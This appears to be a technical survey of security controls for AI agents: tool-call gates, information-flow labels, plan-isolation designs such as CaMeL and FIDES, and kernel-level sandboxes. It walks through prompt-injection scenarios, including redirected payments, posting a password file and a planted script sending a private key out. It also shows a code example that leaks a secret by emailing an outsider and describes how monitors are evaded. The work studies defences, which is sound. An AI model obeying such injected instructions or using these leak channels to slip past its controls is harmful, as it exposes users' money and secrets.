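| Judge at the gate | Calls blocked | Attacks that succeeded | User tasks completed |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 0% | 4.7% | 25.4% |
| 7 billion parameters, threshold 0.7 | 12% | 3.2% | 24.3% |
| 3 billion parameters, threshold 0.5 | 78% | 0.4% | 18.0% |

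The smaller judge's gate stopped nearly all the attacks, but it did so by blocking most of what the agent tried to do. In the office suite, where no attack succeeded even without a gate, it blocked 85% of calls and cut completed tasks from 26.4% to 16.3%. The larger judge's gate interfered much less, but its overall effect on attacks could have been due to chance. The two gates are chosen settings with different thresholds, so comparing them doesn't show that smaller judges are safer.

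In a second run, Ray matched 389 episodes with and without each gate. For the smaller judge, 34 attacks succeeded only without the gate and 5 succeeded only with it. For the larger judge, the numbers were 29 and 22. Ray takes the attacks that succeeded only with a gate as proof that blocking can steer an agent into an attack it would otherwise have avoided. This is plausible, but ordinary variation could explain some of these attacks, since the number that succeeded without a gate changed from 45 to 38 between the two runs.

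### What a refusal reveals

A refusal can also leak information. Suppose an injected instruction tells the assistant to open a colleague's disciplinary file, and the gate returns "permission denied". If the file didn't exist, the gate would have returned "not found". The assistant now has good evidence that the colleague has a disciplinary file, and can mention it in an email. No protected text entered the context, so a gate that scans the email for protected text will find nothing. A series of such requests could map out which files exist and which are protected, much as counts of matching records can reveal a hidden email address.

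*Causality Laundering* proposes treating refusals as data. The gate records each refusal in the graph it uses to track tool outputs, and links it to the agent's next call. The gate blocks any call with such a link. It can't detect whether the refusal influenced the model, so it treats every linked call as influenced.

This design catches an agent that asks for something forbidden and immediately reports the result. It can miss a leak several calls later, and it can block a harmless call that follows a refusal. The second error is serious for an agent that is supposed to respond to a block by finding a safer approach, because the gate will stop the safer call. The design has also had little testing. Its evaluation used three hand-built attacks, only one of which involved a refusal, and did not measure how often the gate would block legitimate work.

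A simpler precaution is to give the same reply whether something is forbidden or doesn't exist. Out-of-Band Policy Enforcement similarly tells the agent only that the call failed. Either way, the agent loses the explanation that helped it recover in the *LEANGUARD* tests. In most sessions, Claude Code returns only the name of the rule that the judge applied, such as "Data Exfiltration", without a written explanation. An operator could also vary the reply by rule, explaining a missing confirmation in full but not why a personnel file is unavailable.

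## Tracking where data came from

Suppose a gate receives a call to transfer 40 dollars to account 7731. The user may have typed that account number, or the model may have copied it from an email that an attacker wrote. The call is identical in both cases, so the gate needs a record of where each value came from. Security engineers keep such records with information-flow control, a technique from the 1970s. It labels data at its source, carries the labels through every computation, and checks them before a value leaves the system.

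### Labels and how they spread

*Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) gives each label two parts. The integrity part marks data as untrusted if an outsider could have written it and trusted otherwise. The confidentiality part lists the people who may read it. Neither part depends on the content, so an honest email from a stranger gets the same untrusted label as a forged one.

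When a program combines two values *x* and *y* into a new value *z*, the result is untrusted if either input is, and only people who may read both inputs may read it:

readers(*z*) = readers(*x*) ∩ readers(*y*).

If Ana, Ben and Carl may read a contract, and Ben, Carl and Dina may read a price list, then only Ben and Carl may read a summary of both. Before an email containing *z* goes out, the gate checks that every recipient is in readers(*z*). Text from a customer record keeps its list of permitted readers, so the gate can enforce part of the personal-data rule by looking up that list instead of estimating whether a draft contains personal data. This only works for data from a labelled source. Costa and colleagues treat the user's own messages as trusted and public by default, so a customer's address that the user typed into the chat would pass the check.

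Labels are harder to carry through a language model, because nobody can reliably tell which parts of the context shaped its output. The safe rule is to give the output the combined label of everything in the context, so after the model has read one untrusted email, every tool call it proposes is untrusted. When Costa and colleagues added checks based on these labels to an ordinary GPT-4o agent, the share of AgentDojo's banking tasks it completed with no attack present fell from 98.8% to 37.5%.

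### An invoice that supplies the account number

Suppose the user writes "Pay the plumber's invoice from this morning's email", and the policy lets untrusted data set the amount of a transfer but not the payee.

1. The request enters the context with a trusted label.
2. The mail tool returns the message, and code around the tool labels its body untrusted, because anyone can send an email.
3. A model extracts the account number, 7731, and the amount, 40. Both values inherit the untrusted label.
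4. The assistant proposes a transfer with these two arguments.
5. The gate accepts the untrusted amount, which the payment cap limits anyway, but finds an untrusted account number and blocks the call.

The gate would block this call even if the plumber wrote every word of the email. An operator who wants genuine invoices paid has to find a trusted source for the account number. The assistant could look up the plumber in a list of payees that the user saved earlier, and then a forged email could change only the amount. The gate could also hold the payment until the user confirms the account. A third option is endorsement, an explicit instruction to treat a particular untrusted value as trusted. This would allow the payment, but it would also allow payment of a forged invoice.

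The gate must also track where the decision to make a transfer came from. If the model proposed the transfer after reading the email, an instruction hidden in the email may have prompted it, so the safe rule is to mark the whole call as untrusted. The designer can keep the decision trusted only by keeping the email away from the model that makes it.

### One model plans and another reads

The software developer Simon Willison proposed such a separation in 2023 and called it "dual LLM". A privileged model receives the user's request and chooses the tool calls, but never receives untrusted text. A quarantined model reads the untrusted text and answers questions about it, but has no tools. The surrounding program stores each answer in a variable, and the privileged model handles only the variable's name. For example, the privileged model can ask for a summary of `email_1` and have it sent to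 the user's manager without the email or the summary entering its context.

An injection in the email can therefore corrupt the summary but can't add a recipient or call another tool. The pattern protects the choice of actions but not the values those actions use. In the invoice example, a hidden instruction to make a second payment would have no effect, but an instruction to report a different account number could still redirect the original payment.

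### CaMeL

CaMeL, which researchers at Google DeepMind and ETH Zurich published in 2025, adds labels to this pattern and has the privileged model write its whole plan as a program. For the invoice, the program might be:

```
email = read_latest_email(sender="plumber")
invoice = ask_quarantined_model("Extract account and amount", email)
transfer(account=invoice.account, amount=invoice.amount)
```

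The model writes this code before anything fetches the email, and an interpreter runs it line by line. The interpreter attaches capabilities to every value. *CaMeLoT* (2026) describes these as records of the value's sources and who may read it. At each tool call, the interpreter passes the arguments and their capabilities to a policy function, which allows or denies the call.

*Can CaMeLs Talk?* (Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues, 2026) calls the central guarantee control-flow integrity, meaning that untrusted data can determine which of the program's existing branches runs but cannot add a new one. The policy functions deal separately with harmful values, such as the attacker's account number in the third line.

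The policies stop more attacks but make many tasks impossible. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *The LLMbda Calculus*, reran CaMeL on AgentDojo's banking tasks with two models, GPT-5.2 and MiMo-v2.5. With the policies off, 5 of 622 completed attack runs succeeded, and CaMeL completed 67% and 71% of ordinary tasks. With the policies on, none of 588 attacks succeeded, but both models completed only 37.5% of ordinary tasks. The suite has just 16 tasks, so these percentages are imprecise. Still, the models' identical scores with the policies on suggest that the policies limited how many tasks they could complete, and that a better model would not have helped much.

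Fixing the plan in advance may explain much of the low attack rate without policies. In about two-thirds of the combinations of task and attack, the attack needs a tool call that a plan for the user's task would never contain. A fixed plan defeats nearly all of these attacks, regardless of the labels. Benchmark totals don't separate these easy cases from attacks in which the planned calls could serve the attacker.

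Small models have a different problem, which is writing the program. In *CapLite*, Xu, Liu and Nakayama (2026) ran CaMeL with 15 open models, 13 of which had at most 12 billion parameters. Only 20 of 13,935 attacks succeeded, compared with 2,322 against an undefended agent. But CaMeL completed 24.9% of ordinary tasks, while the undefended agent completed 59.4%, and it used 93,700 tokens per task instead of 28,000. One model, Granite-4.2-8B, failed to produce a runnable program in 68% of runs, even after up to ten attempts at repair.

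Xu and colleagues built a simpler design in which the model lists the actions that would change anything, instead of writing a program. It makes this list before reading any data, and ordinary code then checks that every recipient, amount and account number appears in the user's own request. In the invoice example, the design would stop and ask the user about account 7731. No attack succeeded in the same 13,935 runs, and the design used 17,100 tokens per task, but it completed only 28.1% of ordinary tasks. That figure somewhat understates its usefulness because the evaluation counted every request for confirmation as a failure, but these requests made up only 8–12% of the failures. More often, the small model had left a necessary action off its list.

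CaMeL's guarantee also applies to only one agent at a time. Peters-Gill and colleagues connected three CaMeL agents, an orchestrator that could call a database agent and a notification agent, and asked them to send a summary of job applicants to a colleague called Julie. The database agent and the orchestrator correctly treated an injected instruction in the database as untrusted data. But the orchestrator then inserted the summary into its request to the notification agent, which treated the request as coming from its user. The notification agent's planner wrote an extra line that emailed the applicants' details to an outsider.

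The proposed remedy is a protocol that sends instructions and untrusted values between agents through separate channels. On a benchmark with several agents, attacks succeeded 12.9% of the time without CaMeL, 0.2% with separate CaMeL agents and 0.0% with the new protocol. The experiments used no policy functions, so they tested only the control of actions.

### FIDES

FIDES, the system that Costa and colleagues built at Microsoft, keeps the ordinary agent loop, in which the planner model chooses each tool call after the previous one returns. It hides a value behind a variable name only if reading the value would make the context less trusted. A list of bank transactions might reach the planner with the dates and amounts visible and the descriptions hidden. The planner can send hidden values to a quarantined model with no tools, or read them itself and accept the untrusted label, which then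 restricts what it may do.

Costa and colleagues tested FIDES on AgentDojo in 2025. Without label checks, they counted 152 genuine successful attacks against an ordinary agent and 21 against FIDES. With the checks on, they counted none against either. AgentDojo's own scoring recorded three successes against FIDES with the checks on, but the researchers rejected all three after reading the runs. In some such cases, the benchmark had counted an attack as successful even though the policy had blocked the call.

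The checks reduce FIDES's performance less than the ordinary agent's, except on travel tasks. The figures below are for GPT-4o with no attack.

| AgentDojo suite | Ordinary agent, no checks | Ordinary agent, label checks | FIDES, label checks |
|---|---|---|---|
| Office | 75.0% | 37.0% | 59.0% |
| Travel | 70.0% | 73.0% | 41.0% |
| Banking | 98.8% | 37.5% | 52.5% |
| Slack | 93.3% | 20.0% | 47.6% |

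Some of the loss came from GPT-4o handling variables badly. With o1, a stronger model at the time, FIDES completed 68% of the travel tasks. Both models are now old, and current ones would probably lose less. Newer models would not fix a weakness in the security result, however. The researchers marked a field as untrusted if any AgentDojo attack used it, so their labels fitted the attacks perfectly, whereas an operator has to guess which fields an attacker might reach.

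Microsoft has since turned FIDES into a product feature, which is still marked experimental. Microsoft's *Stop prompt injection from hijacking your agent* (2026) describes an agent that sorts bug reports on GitHub, a site where programmers share code. A public report contains a hidden instruction to read a file of passwords and post it as a comment. Even if the model follows the instruction, the gate blocks the comment, because the file's private label has spread to the context and the comment tool accepts only public data.

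In this release, a tool that a developer forgets to label counts as trusted and public. Microsoft has asked developers whether to reverse this default, which is riskier than Cedar's default denial. An untrusted item that the model has read taints the rest of the run unless the developer removes it.

### Influence that labels miss

Labels follow copied and combined values fairly well, but information can also travel through a program's choices. Garby and colleagues found that CaMeL's interpreter misses some of these, even though it does track the conditions under which a line runs. In this version of their example, the balance is secret and the first two variables start out public:

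```
rich = True
tmp = True
if balance > threshold: tmp = False
if tmp: rich = False
if rich: send_email("outsider@example.com", "rich!")
```

If the balance is high, the third line sets `tmp` to false and labels it secret. The interpreter then skips the assignment in the fourth line. Because it only labels assignments that it runs, `rich` is still true and public, and the email goes out. If the balance is low, the fourth line sets `rich` to false and no email goes out, so the outsider learns whether the balance is high.

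One such email reveals a single bit, but repeated attempts can reveal more. CaMeL's interpreter runs inside an ordinary retry loop that doesn't track labels, and whether the policy blocked an attempt can depend on a secret. Ten yes-or-no answers are enough to find a whole-dollar balance below 1,024. An outside attacker would struggle to exploit either gap, since CaMeL's planner never reads the attacker's text. The gaps matter more if the planner itself is compromised, and a governance layer should still work in that case.

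FIDES deliberately leaves this channel open. Its formal guarantee, explicit secrecy, covers secrets that flow directly into outputs but not what an observer can infer from the agent's sequence of calls. Costa and colleagues argue that closing the channel would mean forbidding almost any public action after the agent reads something secret. The scheduling assistant that Pandey and colleagues describe could leak a private reason through the same channel, even if no labelled value reached its offer.

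Garby and colleagues instead designed a small programming language, LLMbda, whose interpreter tracks choices as well as values. They proved in Lean that secrets in any LLMbda program, including one that a model writes at runtime, can affect public outputs only through whether the program finishes. An agent written in LLMbda completed 75% of AgentDojo's ordinary banking tasks with GPT-5.2, and 2 of 1,296 attacks succeeded across three models. The agent enforces only some of CaMeL's policies and lets the planner endorse untrusted data in advance, so its score is not directly comparable with CaMeL's 37.5%. Without endorsement, completion fell from 75% to 62.5% with one model and from 65% to 54% with another.

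Both successful attacks were on a task in which the agent must read a file and pay the bill in it. The attacker had replaced the file's contents with a different payment request. This is the invoice problem again. The planner had endorsed the file because the task was impossible otherwise, and the labels did not distinguish a real bill from a false one. CaMeL's developers consider this attack outside the scope of their design.

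A quarantined model's output can be misleading in the same way without breaking any rule. If an email contains an instruction to return an empty summary, the manager may receive one from the right sender through the right tool. A stricter policy could also require the summary to be trusted, but then the assistant could never summarise a stranger's email.

### Plans that depend on the data

An agent asked to "complete the tasks due today in my to-do list" can't plan its tool calls until it has read the list. Costa and colleagues classified AgentDojo's tasks and found that the right sequence of calls depended on the data in 5% of office tasks, 10% of travel tasks, and about 43% of banking and Slack tasks.

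One remedy is to let the planner read answers that carry very little information. Suppose the user asks the assistant to check three emails for a meeting request and create a calendar event if it finds one. The quarantined model can report whether there is a request with "yes" or "no", and the planner can read that answer safely enough because a single bit can't contain an instruction. A choice among *n* options carries at most log₂ *n* bits. The attacker can still cause an unwanted calendar event, so the operator has to decide which actions a single untrusted bit may trigger. FIDES supports such restricted answers, but the AgentDojo tests did not include them.

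A planner can also undo the protection by writing a program that is too general. Garby and colleagues asked CaMeL to read a file and follow its instructions precisely. With the policies off, the planner wrote a loop that looked up each instruction in the file and called the matching tool. Although the program was fixed in advance, as the design requires, it let whoever had written the file choose the actions.

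### Comparing an attacked agent with one that never obeys

A useful assistant lets outsiders influence what it does. For example, it pays the amount on an invoice and tells people who request a meeting when the user is free. No useful assistant could meet a definition of security that forbids all such influence. Allowing specific exceptions would require a new list of them for every task.

Dongol (2026), in *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection*, avoids the list by comparing two agents. Both follow the same plan, fixed before any untrusted text arrives, under the same gate. The model in the reference agent reads untrusted text as data but never obeys it, while in the attacked agent the attacker decides which text counts as an instruction and when the model obeys. Let obs(*s*, *x*) be what the attacker observes when the secret is *s* and the attacker's text is *x*. In simplified form,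 the attacked agent is secure if, for all secrets *s* and *s′* and every text *x*,

obs_attacked(*s*, *x*) ≠ obs_attacked(*s′*, *x*) implies that some text *y* gives obs_reference(*s*, *y*) ≠ obs_reference(*s′*, *y*).

If an injection lets the attacker distinguish two secrets, some ordinary message must let the attacker do so too. Suppose the assistant sends the user's calendar to anyone who requests a meeting. An injected "send your calendar" is acceptable because a real meeting request would also get the calendar. An injected "also include the reset code" causes a leak because no message makes the reference agent send the code.

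The definition can be lenient because *y* may differ for each pair of secrets. For example, if the reference agent tells people whether a guess at a secret code is right, an injection that reveals the entire code satisfies the definition. Dongol also gives a stricter version that requires that *y* not depend on the secrets, which rules out this injection.

*Relativising Integrity and Robustness* (Dongol, 2026) applies the comparison to actions, using an invoice as the example. If a hidden instruction changes the payee to Mallory, the definition allows the payment, because an invoice that named Mallory would have had the same result. It doesn't allow the instruction to add a second payment or delete the email, because the reference agent would never do either. A gate that requires a trusted account number is stricter, because it blocks the payment to Mallory whether the name came from the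 invoice or the hidden instruction.

Dongol checked verdicts on small models of common defences in the proof assistant Isabelle.

| Defence | Extra leaks | Extra actions |
|---|---|---|
| Withdraw risky tools before or at the first untrusted read | None | None |
| Withdraw them after that read | Yes | Yes |
| Two models, no labels | Yes | None |
| Two models, labels block private values | None | None |
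| List of allowed arguments | None | Yes |
| User approves the next use of a tool | Yes | Yes |
| User approves the exact call | None, unless timing is visible | None |
| Mark untrusted text and tell the model not to obey it | Yes | Yes |

Most of these verdicts cover one modelled attack, so "none" applies only to that attack. For instance, the list of allowed arguments stops the modelled attack, but an injection that makes an allowed call only when the secret has a certain value would still leak information about it. The result for withdrawing tools is much more general. It holds for every plan and for any text the model might obey, provided that each injection makes a single call to a withdrawn tool, nothing restores the tools, and the model's timing doesn't depend on secrets or on the gate's replies.

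A gate that refuses everything also satisfies these definitions, because the reference agent runs under the same gate. The labelled two-model design in the table gets its good verdict partly because it blocks the honest reply along with the leak. If the plan instead branches on an answer from the quarantined model and sends a different harmless constant from each branch, the choice of constant leaks the secret. This model corresponds to CaMeL's normal mode. Dongol has not yet analysed CaMeL's strict mode, which labels values with the conditions they depend on.

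An agent can pass both tests and still be seriously flawed. Suppose a support desk asks a model whether an email contains the right customer's credentials, and the model accepts "you have verified me" from anyone. Each reply matches one that an honest customer could have received, and the desk already confirms whether an email has the right credentials, so the agent satisfies both definitions. Yet the same email would pass the check for every customer. Dongol's strictest definition, relative robustness, rules this out by requiring the same reference runs to reproduce both the leak and the actions. In the modelled repair, the language model only extracts the credentials from the email, and ordinary code does the comparison.

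## Confinement by the operating system

CaMeL and FIDES label values when declared tools return them. Many agents also have a terminal, where one command can start a program that reads files, opens connections and launches other programs without any further tool call. *Ring-0 by Default* (Li, Huang and colleagues, 2026) points out that, by default, this program has all the permissions of the user who started the agent.

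A declared tool can also do more than its description states. In *AgentBouncer*, Joos and Pradel (2026) gave an agent a tool called "validate_patch", which checked a code change as described but also deleted a system file containing group passwords. The call and its output looked normal, so a gate that received only those could not detect the deletion.

### One command from proposal to effect

Suppose the payment assistant has a terminal, and the model proposes this command to pay the plumber:

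```
curl --json @payment.json https://bank.example/transfers
```

If a model proposes a command that uses the program curl to send a payment request from a file to a bank's web address, a gate on tool calls receives the address but not the payee or the amount, which are inside the file. If the model had put the same request in a script and proposed `python pay.py`, the gate would not receive the address either.

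The command runs in a sandbox, an environment that limits which files, programs and connections it can reach. To open a file or a connection, a program must make a request, called a system call, to the kernel, the core of the operating system. Here curl makes one call to open `payment.json`, others to read it, another to connect to the bank's numerical address, and more to send the data. On Linux, Landlock can refuse access to files outside a permitted list, and seccomp can pause a call until a supervising program allows or refuses it. The supervisor can check the file's name and the bank's numerical address, but it can't read the payment in the calls that send it, because curl encrypts the data first.

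An outbound network proxy relays connections between the sandbox and the internet. If the sandbox blocks every other route, curl has to use the proxy. The proxy in *Steerability via constraints* (2026) does not decrypt traffic, so it can allow or refuse `bank.example` by name but can't distinguish a transfer from a balance enquiry. A decrypting proxy can read the payee and the amount before encrypting the request again for the bank, so it could enforce the payment cap. It can also read every password and private document the agent sends, so the operator has to trust it much more.

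The bank will reject the transfer without a valid credential, and a credential broker can keep that credential out of the sandbox. Docker's *Credentials* documentation describes a setup in which the program in the sandbox sends a placeholder, and a proxy on the host computer replaces it with the real credential. If curl reached the bank without going through the proxy, it would have only the placeholder.

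| Component | What it receives | What it can refuse |
|---|---|---|
| Gate on tool calls | The text of the command | The whole command |
| File rules in the sandbox | The path of `payment.json` and the kind of access | Access to the file |
| System-call supervisor | Each call, including the bank's numerical address | One call, while the program keeps running |
| Proxy without decryption | The name `bank.example` | The connection |
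| Proxy with decryption | The full request, with payee and amount | One request |
| Credential broker | The destination and, if it relays the request, the contents | The credential |

A broker can also give the agent a temporary credential. Hartman (2026) recommends this where the service supports it, in *Credential Broker for Agents (CB4A)*, a draft that was submitted to the Internet's main standards body and expired in September. The broker uses the long-lived credential to obtain a token that works for seconds or minutes and covers only the requested task. The agent then contacts the service directly, which avoids the delay and single point of failure of a proxy. But the broker no longer receives the individual requests, so it could not keep the running total for a payment cap, and the relaying broker is better for that rule.

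Hartman also keeps the credentials away from the component that approves requests, so an attacker who takes over that component still can't read them. The agent must state a reason for each request, but the reason is only for later investigations, and the approving component must ignore it.

### The gap in meaning

The operating system is hard to avoid because every program has to use it, whatever language it is written in. But its records contain little about why a program does something. For instance, listing a folder with `ls` often opens the sensitive-looking file `/etc/passwd` just to turn user numbers into names. When Joos and Pradel tested a gate on system calls, this harmless lookup accounted for 79% of the gate's false alarms in runs with an attack.

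The same action can be right for one task and wrong for another. A program that adds a line to the user's terminal start-up file may be doing what the user asked if the request was to make a new program available in the terminal, but the same write is suspicious if the request was to correct a README file. *Kairos* describes how this limits rules at the edge of the sandbox. They can refer only to paths, destinations and the values that cross, which allows fewer rules than at the tool interface, where a rule can refer to the operation and the role of each argument, such as "payee".

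Three designs from late 2026 are meant to recover the missing information. AgentBouncer gives a model the context of each doubtful system call, Tether reconstructs larger actions from the calls, and Kairos postpones the decision until there is more evidence.

### AgentBouncer

AgentBouncer uses seccomp to pause calls that concern files, programs, processes and the network. It then looks for a decision in four places, in this order:

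1. The model's earlier decisions on identical requests in the same run.
2. A profile of 60 standing permissions, such as running the programs in `/bin`.
3. Permissions that the model has extended to a whole folder or web address prefix.
4. The model itself.

The model receives the user's task, the tool call, the agent's stated reason and the requested access. It judges how necessary and how safe the access is. It must refuse an unsafe request even if the task requires it, and it must be more confident that a request is safe when the need for it is less clear. A refused call fails with a permission error while the rest of the program continues. In the "validate_patch" case, the deletion failed and the agent still finished its task.

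The profile and the stored decisions make this practical. An average task produced 28,167 requests, and the model decided fewer than eight of them. Sending every request to the model, at 3.3 seconds each, would have taken more than 25 hours per task.

AgentBouncer blocks all outside connections except those through its own decrypting proxy, and then applies the same four steps to each web request.

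Joos and Pradel combined 85 attack goals, such as deleting system files or sending data to an outside server, with four ways of delivering them: text in the task description, a malicious tool, a script already on the machine, and code that runs with the project's own tests. In each of the 340 resulting cases, the agent was also fixing a real software bug. OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Luna was both the agent and the judge.

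| Defence | Attacks that succeeded | Bugs fixed, no attack |
|---|---|---|
| None | 99.4% | 71.5% |
| Fixed rules on tool calls (AgentSpec) | 28.8% | 63.5% |
| Model compares tool calls with a plan (Drift) | 83.5% | 67.1% |
| Classifier on tool calls (Llama Guard 4) | 11.5% | 1.2% |
| Model reviews system events afterwards (AgentSentinel) | 33.8% | 76.5% |
| AgentBouncer's profile without the model | 0% | 8.2% |
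| AgentBouncer | 10.6% | 72.9% |

The classifier stopped about as many attacks as AgentBouncer, but only by blocking most of what the agent tried to do. AgentSentinel responds to a harmful event by killing the program, but in 24 attacks the full damage had already occurred by then. The profile alone stopped every attack, but it also stopped the agent from writing to the project's files.

AgentBouncer's protection had little effect on the number of bugs fixed, but it increased the average task time from 60 to 108 seconds. AgentBouncer wrongly refused something in 3.4% of harmless tool calls, but only 0.25% of harmless calls failed as a result, because most programs can keep running when a minor request fails.

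Most of the 36 successful attacks consisted of steps that were not clearly harmful by themselves, such as reading a file that might be sensitive. Of the 20 attacks involving the terminal start-up file, 5 succeeded because the model received the file's path but not the text that the program wrote to it. Two of the 36 succeeded because of stored decisions. In one, the model had allowed a harmless read and extended the permission to an entire system folder, so the permission also covered the attacker's later read.

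The judge also receives text that an attacker can influence. Unlike the judge in Claude Code's auto mode, it reads the agent's explanation for each call. Attacks that put text into the task description succeeded 14.1% of the time, compared with 7.1% for the others. All 340 attacks were fixed in advance, so AgentBouncer wasn't tested against an attacker who adapts to it.

### Tether

Tether runs a command first and decides afterwards whether to keep its changes. The command reads the real files, but any changes go to a temporary layer. A tracer records the system calls, and a proxy holds each outgoing request until the policy engine has approved everything the command has done so far. If the engine approves all the actions, Tether applies the changes to the real files. Otherwise it discards them.

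System calls don't show whether the data a program writes came from a file it read earlier. Tether therefore treats the data as copied and gives the new file the label of the old one. This causes some false alarms but avoids missing copies made through the calls it traces. In an example from *Tether*, the file `servers.csv` is sensitive, and the policy allows uploads only of public files.

1. The agent uploads `report.txt`. The file is public, so the engine allows it.
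2. The agent copies `servers.csv` over `report.txt`. The engine allows the copy and labels `report.txt` sensitive.
3. The agent repeats the upload command from the first step, and this time the engine refuses it.

A gate that read only the command text would have to treat the two uploads alike. The label also persists through any number of intermediate copies. In Dogwood, the AWS language for rules about earlier actions, an operator would need another rule for each extra copy, or a broad rule that also blocks harmless uploads.

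The test policy contained 24 rules. A language model wrote proofs that the policy has seven properties in runs of any length, and Lean checked the proofs. One property is that data labelled secret never enters the agent's context. The proofs don't cover the inference of actions, so the researchers tested it separately. They generated random chains of file operations, carried them out in many different ways, and compared Tether's verdicts with the known answers. They also had a model attack the system and fixed the gaps it found. The attacks' success rate fell from 40% to zero over three versions.

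The main evaluation replayed recorded runs from two benchmarks in system administration and software engineering. Tether stopped all 344 harmful runs and interfered with 74 of 1,590 harmless ones (4.7%). In 50 of those 74, the agent had edited a protected file that the task did not mention. In another 17, commands such as a search through the whole disk had opened sensitive files. Claude Code's auto mode, with Claude Sonnet 5 as the judge, stopped 91.6% of the same harmful runs and interfered with 9.7% of the harmless ones. When given Tether's policy as text, auto mode stopped 89.2% of the harmful runs and interfered with 3.5% of the harmless ones.

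The comparison favours Tether because it includes only runs whose actions Tether can model. Among the other runs that the researchers could replay, 28.2% on one benchmark and 22.1% on the other would have required a judgement about content. For example, an agent that inserts malicious code into a file it may edit breaks no rule about where data flows. Tether also can't yet follow background programs or database queries in detail, though it can block them outright. The researchers refined the policy by testing it on benchmark runs, so an operator with a new policy should expect a false-alarm rate above 4.7%.

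The evaluation used recorded runs, so it can't show how many tasks a live agent would complete after a refusal. The paper also gives no figure for delay, but it reports that the tracing tool slowed the experiments considerably, and it suggests faster replacements.

### Kairos

Tether settles the effects of each command before the next one runs, whereas Kairos can hold an effect while the agent takes several more steps. Kairos runs the agent in a small virtual machine, a simulated computer with its own kernel. Changes to the project folder go to a staging layer, and web requests go through a proxy that decrypts them.

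The policy releases an effect if the values that control it, such as a web address or a recipient, match values from a trusted source, and if the destination is allowed to receive the data. It refuses whatever an explicit rule forbids and defers the rest to a person or model, called the oracle, to decide. The oracle can't override a refusal.

The main example in *Kairos* involves a script that runs whenever a programmer saves a version of the code. While setting up a project, an agent reads an online guide with instructions to install such a script. Many legitimate guides include the same step, so blocking the file would disrupt ordinary work. Kairos puts the file in the staging layer and lets the agent continue. When the agent saves its code, the script runs and tries to send the user's private key to an outsider. The policy blocks the request, and the oracle discards the file because there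 is now evidence of what the script does.

An ordinary gate could also have refused to send the key, but by then it would already have let the script into the project. The operator's rule is that no file may remain if a program in it later attempts something forbidden. A gate whose decisions are final can't enforce this rule, because the evidence arrives after the decision. An edit automaton can, because it is a monitor that can suppress an action and insert it later. But it helps only while it is holding the action back, so a script that does nothing suspicious until after its release will remain in the project.

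Kairos can hold a request that changes something elsewhere, such as a payment, if the agent needs only an acknowledgement. It gives the agent a stand-in reply so that the agent can continue. If the agent requests a web page, Kairos has to decide at once, because the agent can't continue without the contents. Kairos must decide on a held request before anything based on the stand-in reply leaves the machine.

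A staging area cannot recall data that has already left the system. *Agent libOS* (2026), which describes another system for controlling what agents do, notes that the system cannot control what an outside service does with data after receiving it.

The researchers tested Kairos on AgentDojo with GPT-4.1 as both the agent and the oracle. Attack success fell from 47.0% to 2.7%, and the agent completed 85.1% of ordinary tasks, compared with 82.7% without a defence. When they made Kairos refuse everything the policy would have deferred, attack success stayed about the same, but the agent completed only 42.7% of ordinary tasks. The policy therefore provided most of the security, and deferring decisions kept the agent useful.

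Performance dropped more on open-ended tasks. On AgentDyn, a benchmark in which the agent discovers the necessary steps as it works, attack success was 1.7%, compared with a published 37.8% for an undefended agent. But with an attack present, the agent completed 37.1% of tasks instead of 55.5%. Success fell to 90% of its usual rate on tasks that continued past one held effect, and to 62% on tasks that continued past two or more. In a third test, an attacker that rewrote its injections over six rounds succeeded in 8.8% of cases. The attacks that still succeeded involved tasks in which the user had told the agent to follow a document, much like the payment request that defeated the labels in LLMbda.

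These benchmarks only simulate tools, so Kairos ran on them through an adapter that supplied each tool's name and arguments. A real deployment would supply only file operations and web requests. The results therefore support the idea of holding effects, but they don't test whether the policy and the oracle can handle the gap in meaning between those operations and the tool calls behind them. The researchers measured the real mechanism's delay at about 1.9 milliseconds per file operation and 1.2 per web request. This excludes the oracle's model calls, which increased token use by 17.7% in runs without an attack.

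### If a trusted component fails

All three designs depend on components that have to work correctly, but some failures do more damage than others.

| Design | Component | If it fails |
|---|---|---|
| AgentBouncer | Kernel or supervising program | Calls can take effect without a check |
| AgentBouncer | Model judge | A harmful call can go through, and a stored decision can repeat the mistake until the run ends |
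| Tether | Kernel, tracer, temporary layer or proxy | Effects can escape before the policy engine decides |
| Tether | Inference of actions | The engine can allow an upload that the policy forbids |
| Tether | Lean | The policy may lack the properties that the proofs are meant to establish |
| Kairos | Host computer, virtual machine or monitor | Effects can escape without a check |
| Kairos | Matching of values to sources | Sensitive data that the agent has disguised can pass as public |
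| Kairos | Oracle | A deferred effect can go through, but nothing that a rule forbids |

The policies in the Kairos tests contained no rules that refused an effect outright, so the limit on the oracle in the last row did not affect the results. Kairos also leaves the connection to the model's provider open and assumes that the provider does not help the attacker.

Agents have already escaped from several kinds of sandbox, so it matters which protections still hold after an escape. *Airlock* (Abdollahi, Al Sadi and colleagues, 2026) starts from OpenShell, Nvidia's sandbox for agents, in which a supervisor outside the sandbox checks each connection, adds the credential and opens the connection itself. *Airlock* puts the agent and the supervisor in separate virtual machines and uses processor features to protect each machine's memory from the other machine and from the host's operating system.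 The agent's machine has no disk or network connection of its own. Even if the agent takes over its machine's kernel, every file and web request still has to go through the supervisor. If the agent found another route to the internet, it would still lack the user's credentials.

The supervisor's machine, the processor and its firmware must still be trusted. An attacker who takes over the supervisor's machine can bypass the rules and get the credentials. The log of earlier actions survives because Airlock copies it to an outside ledger where entries can be added but not changed. Each new encrypted web connection has to wait until its entry is in the ledger, because a connection can't be undone. File accesses don't wait, so the attacker could erase the last few seconds of file-access records.

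Abdollahi and colleagues found that file performance and the delay of short messages each worsened by less than 15%, while network capacity fell by half or more. No commercial processor had the necessary Arm features when they ran the tests, so they used a small board that imitates the features in software. The losses on real hardware may differ.

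## Filters on prompts and answers

Suppose someone asks a chatbot how to make a nerve agent, and the model writes a correct answer. A gate on tool calls or a sandbox would not stop the answer, because the model has called no tool and opened no file. The text itself is dangerous, and the operator cannot take it back once the user has read it, so the operator can intervene only before the prompt reaches the model or before the answer reaches the user.

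### Input, output and exchange classifiers

Usually, a wrapper sends every message through one or more classifiers. An input classifier scores the prompt. If the score is too high, the wrapper refuses the request or passes it to a less capable model. Otherwise, an output classifier scores the answer every few tokens as the model writes it. If the score crosses a threshold, the wrapper cuts the answer off, though the user keeps whatever has already appeared on the screen. The wrapper could hold back the whole answer until the check is complete, but the user would wait much longer for the first word. Anthropic can run several classifiers alongside a conversation, each for a particular kind of harm.

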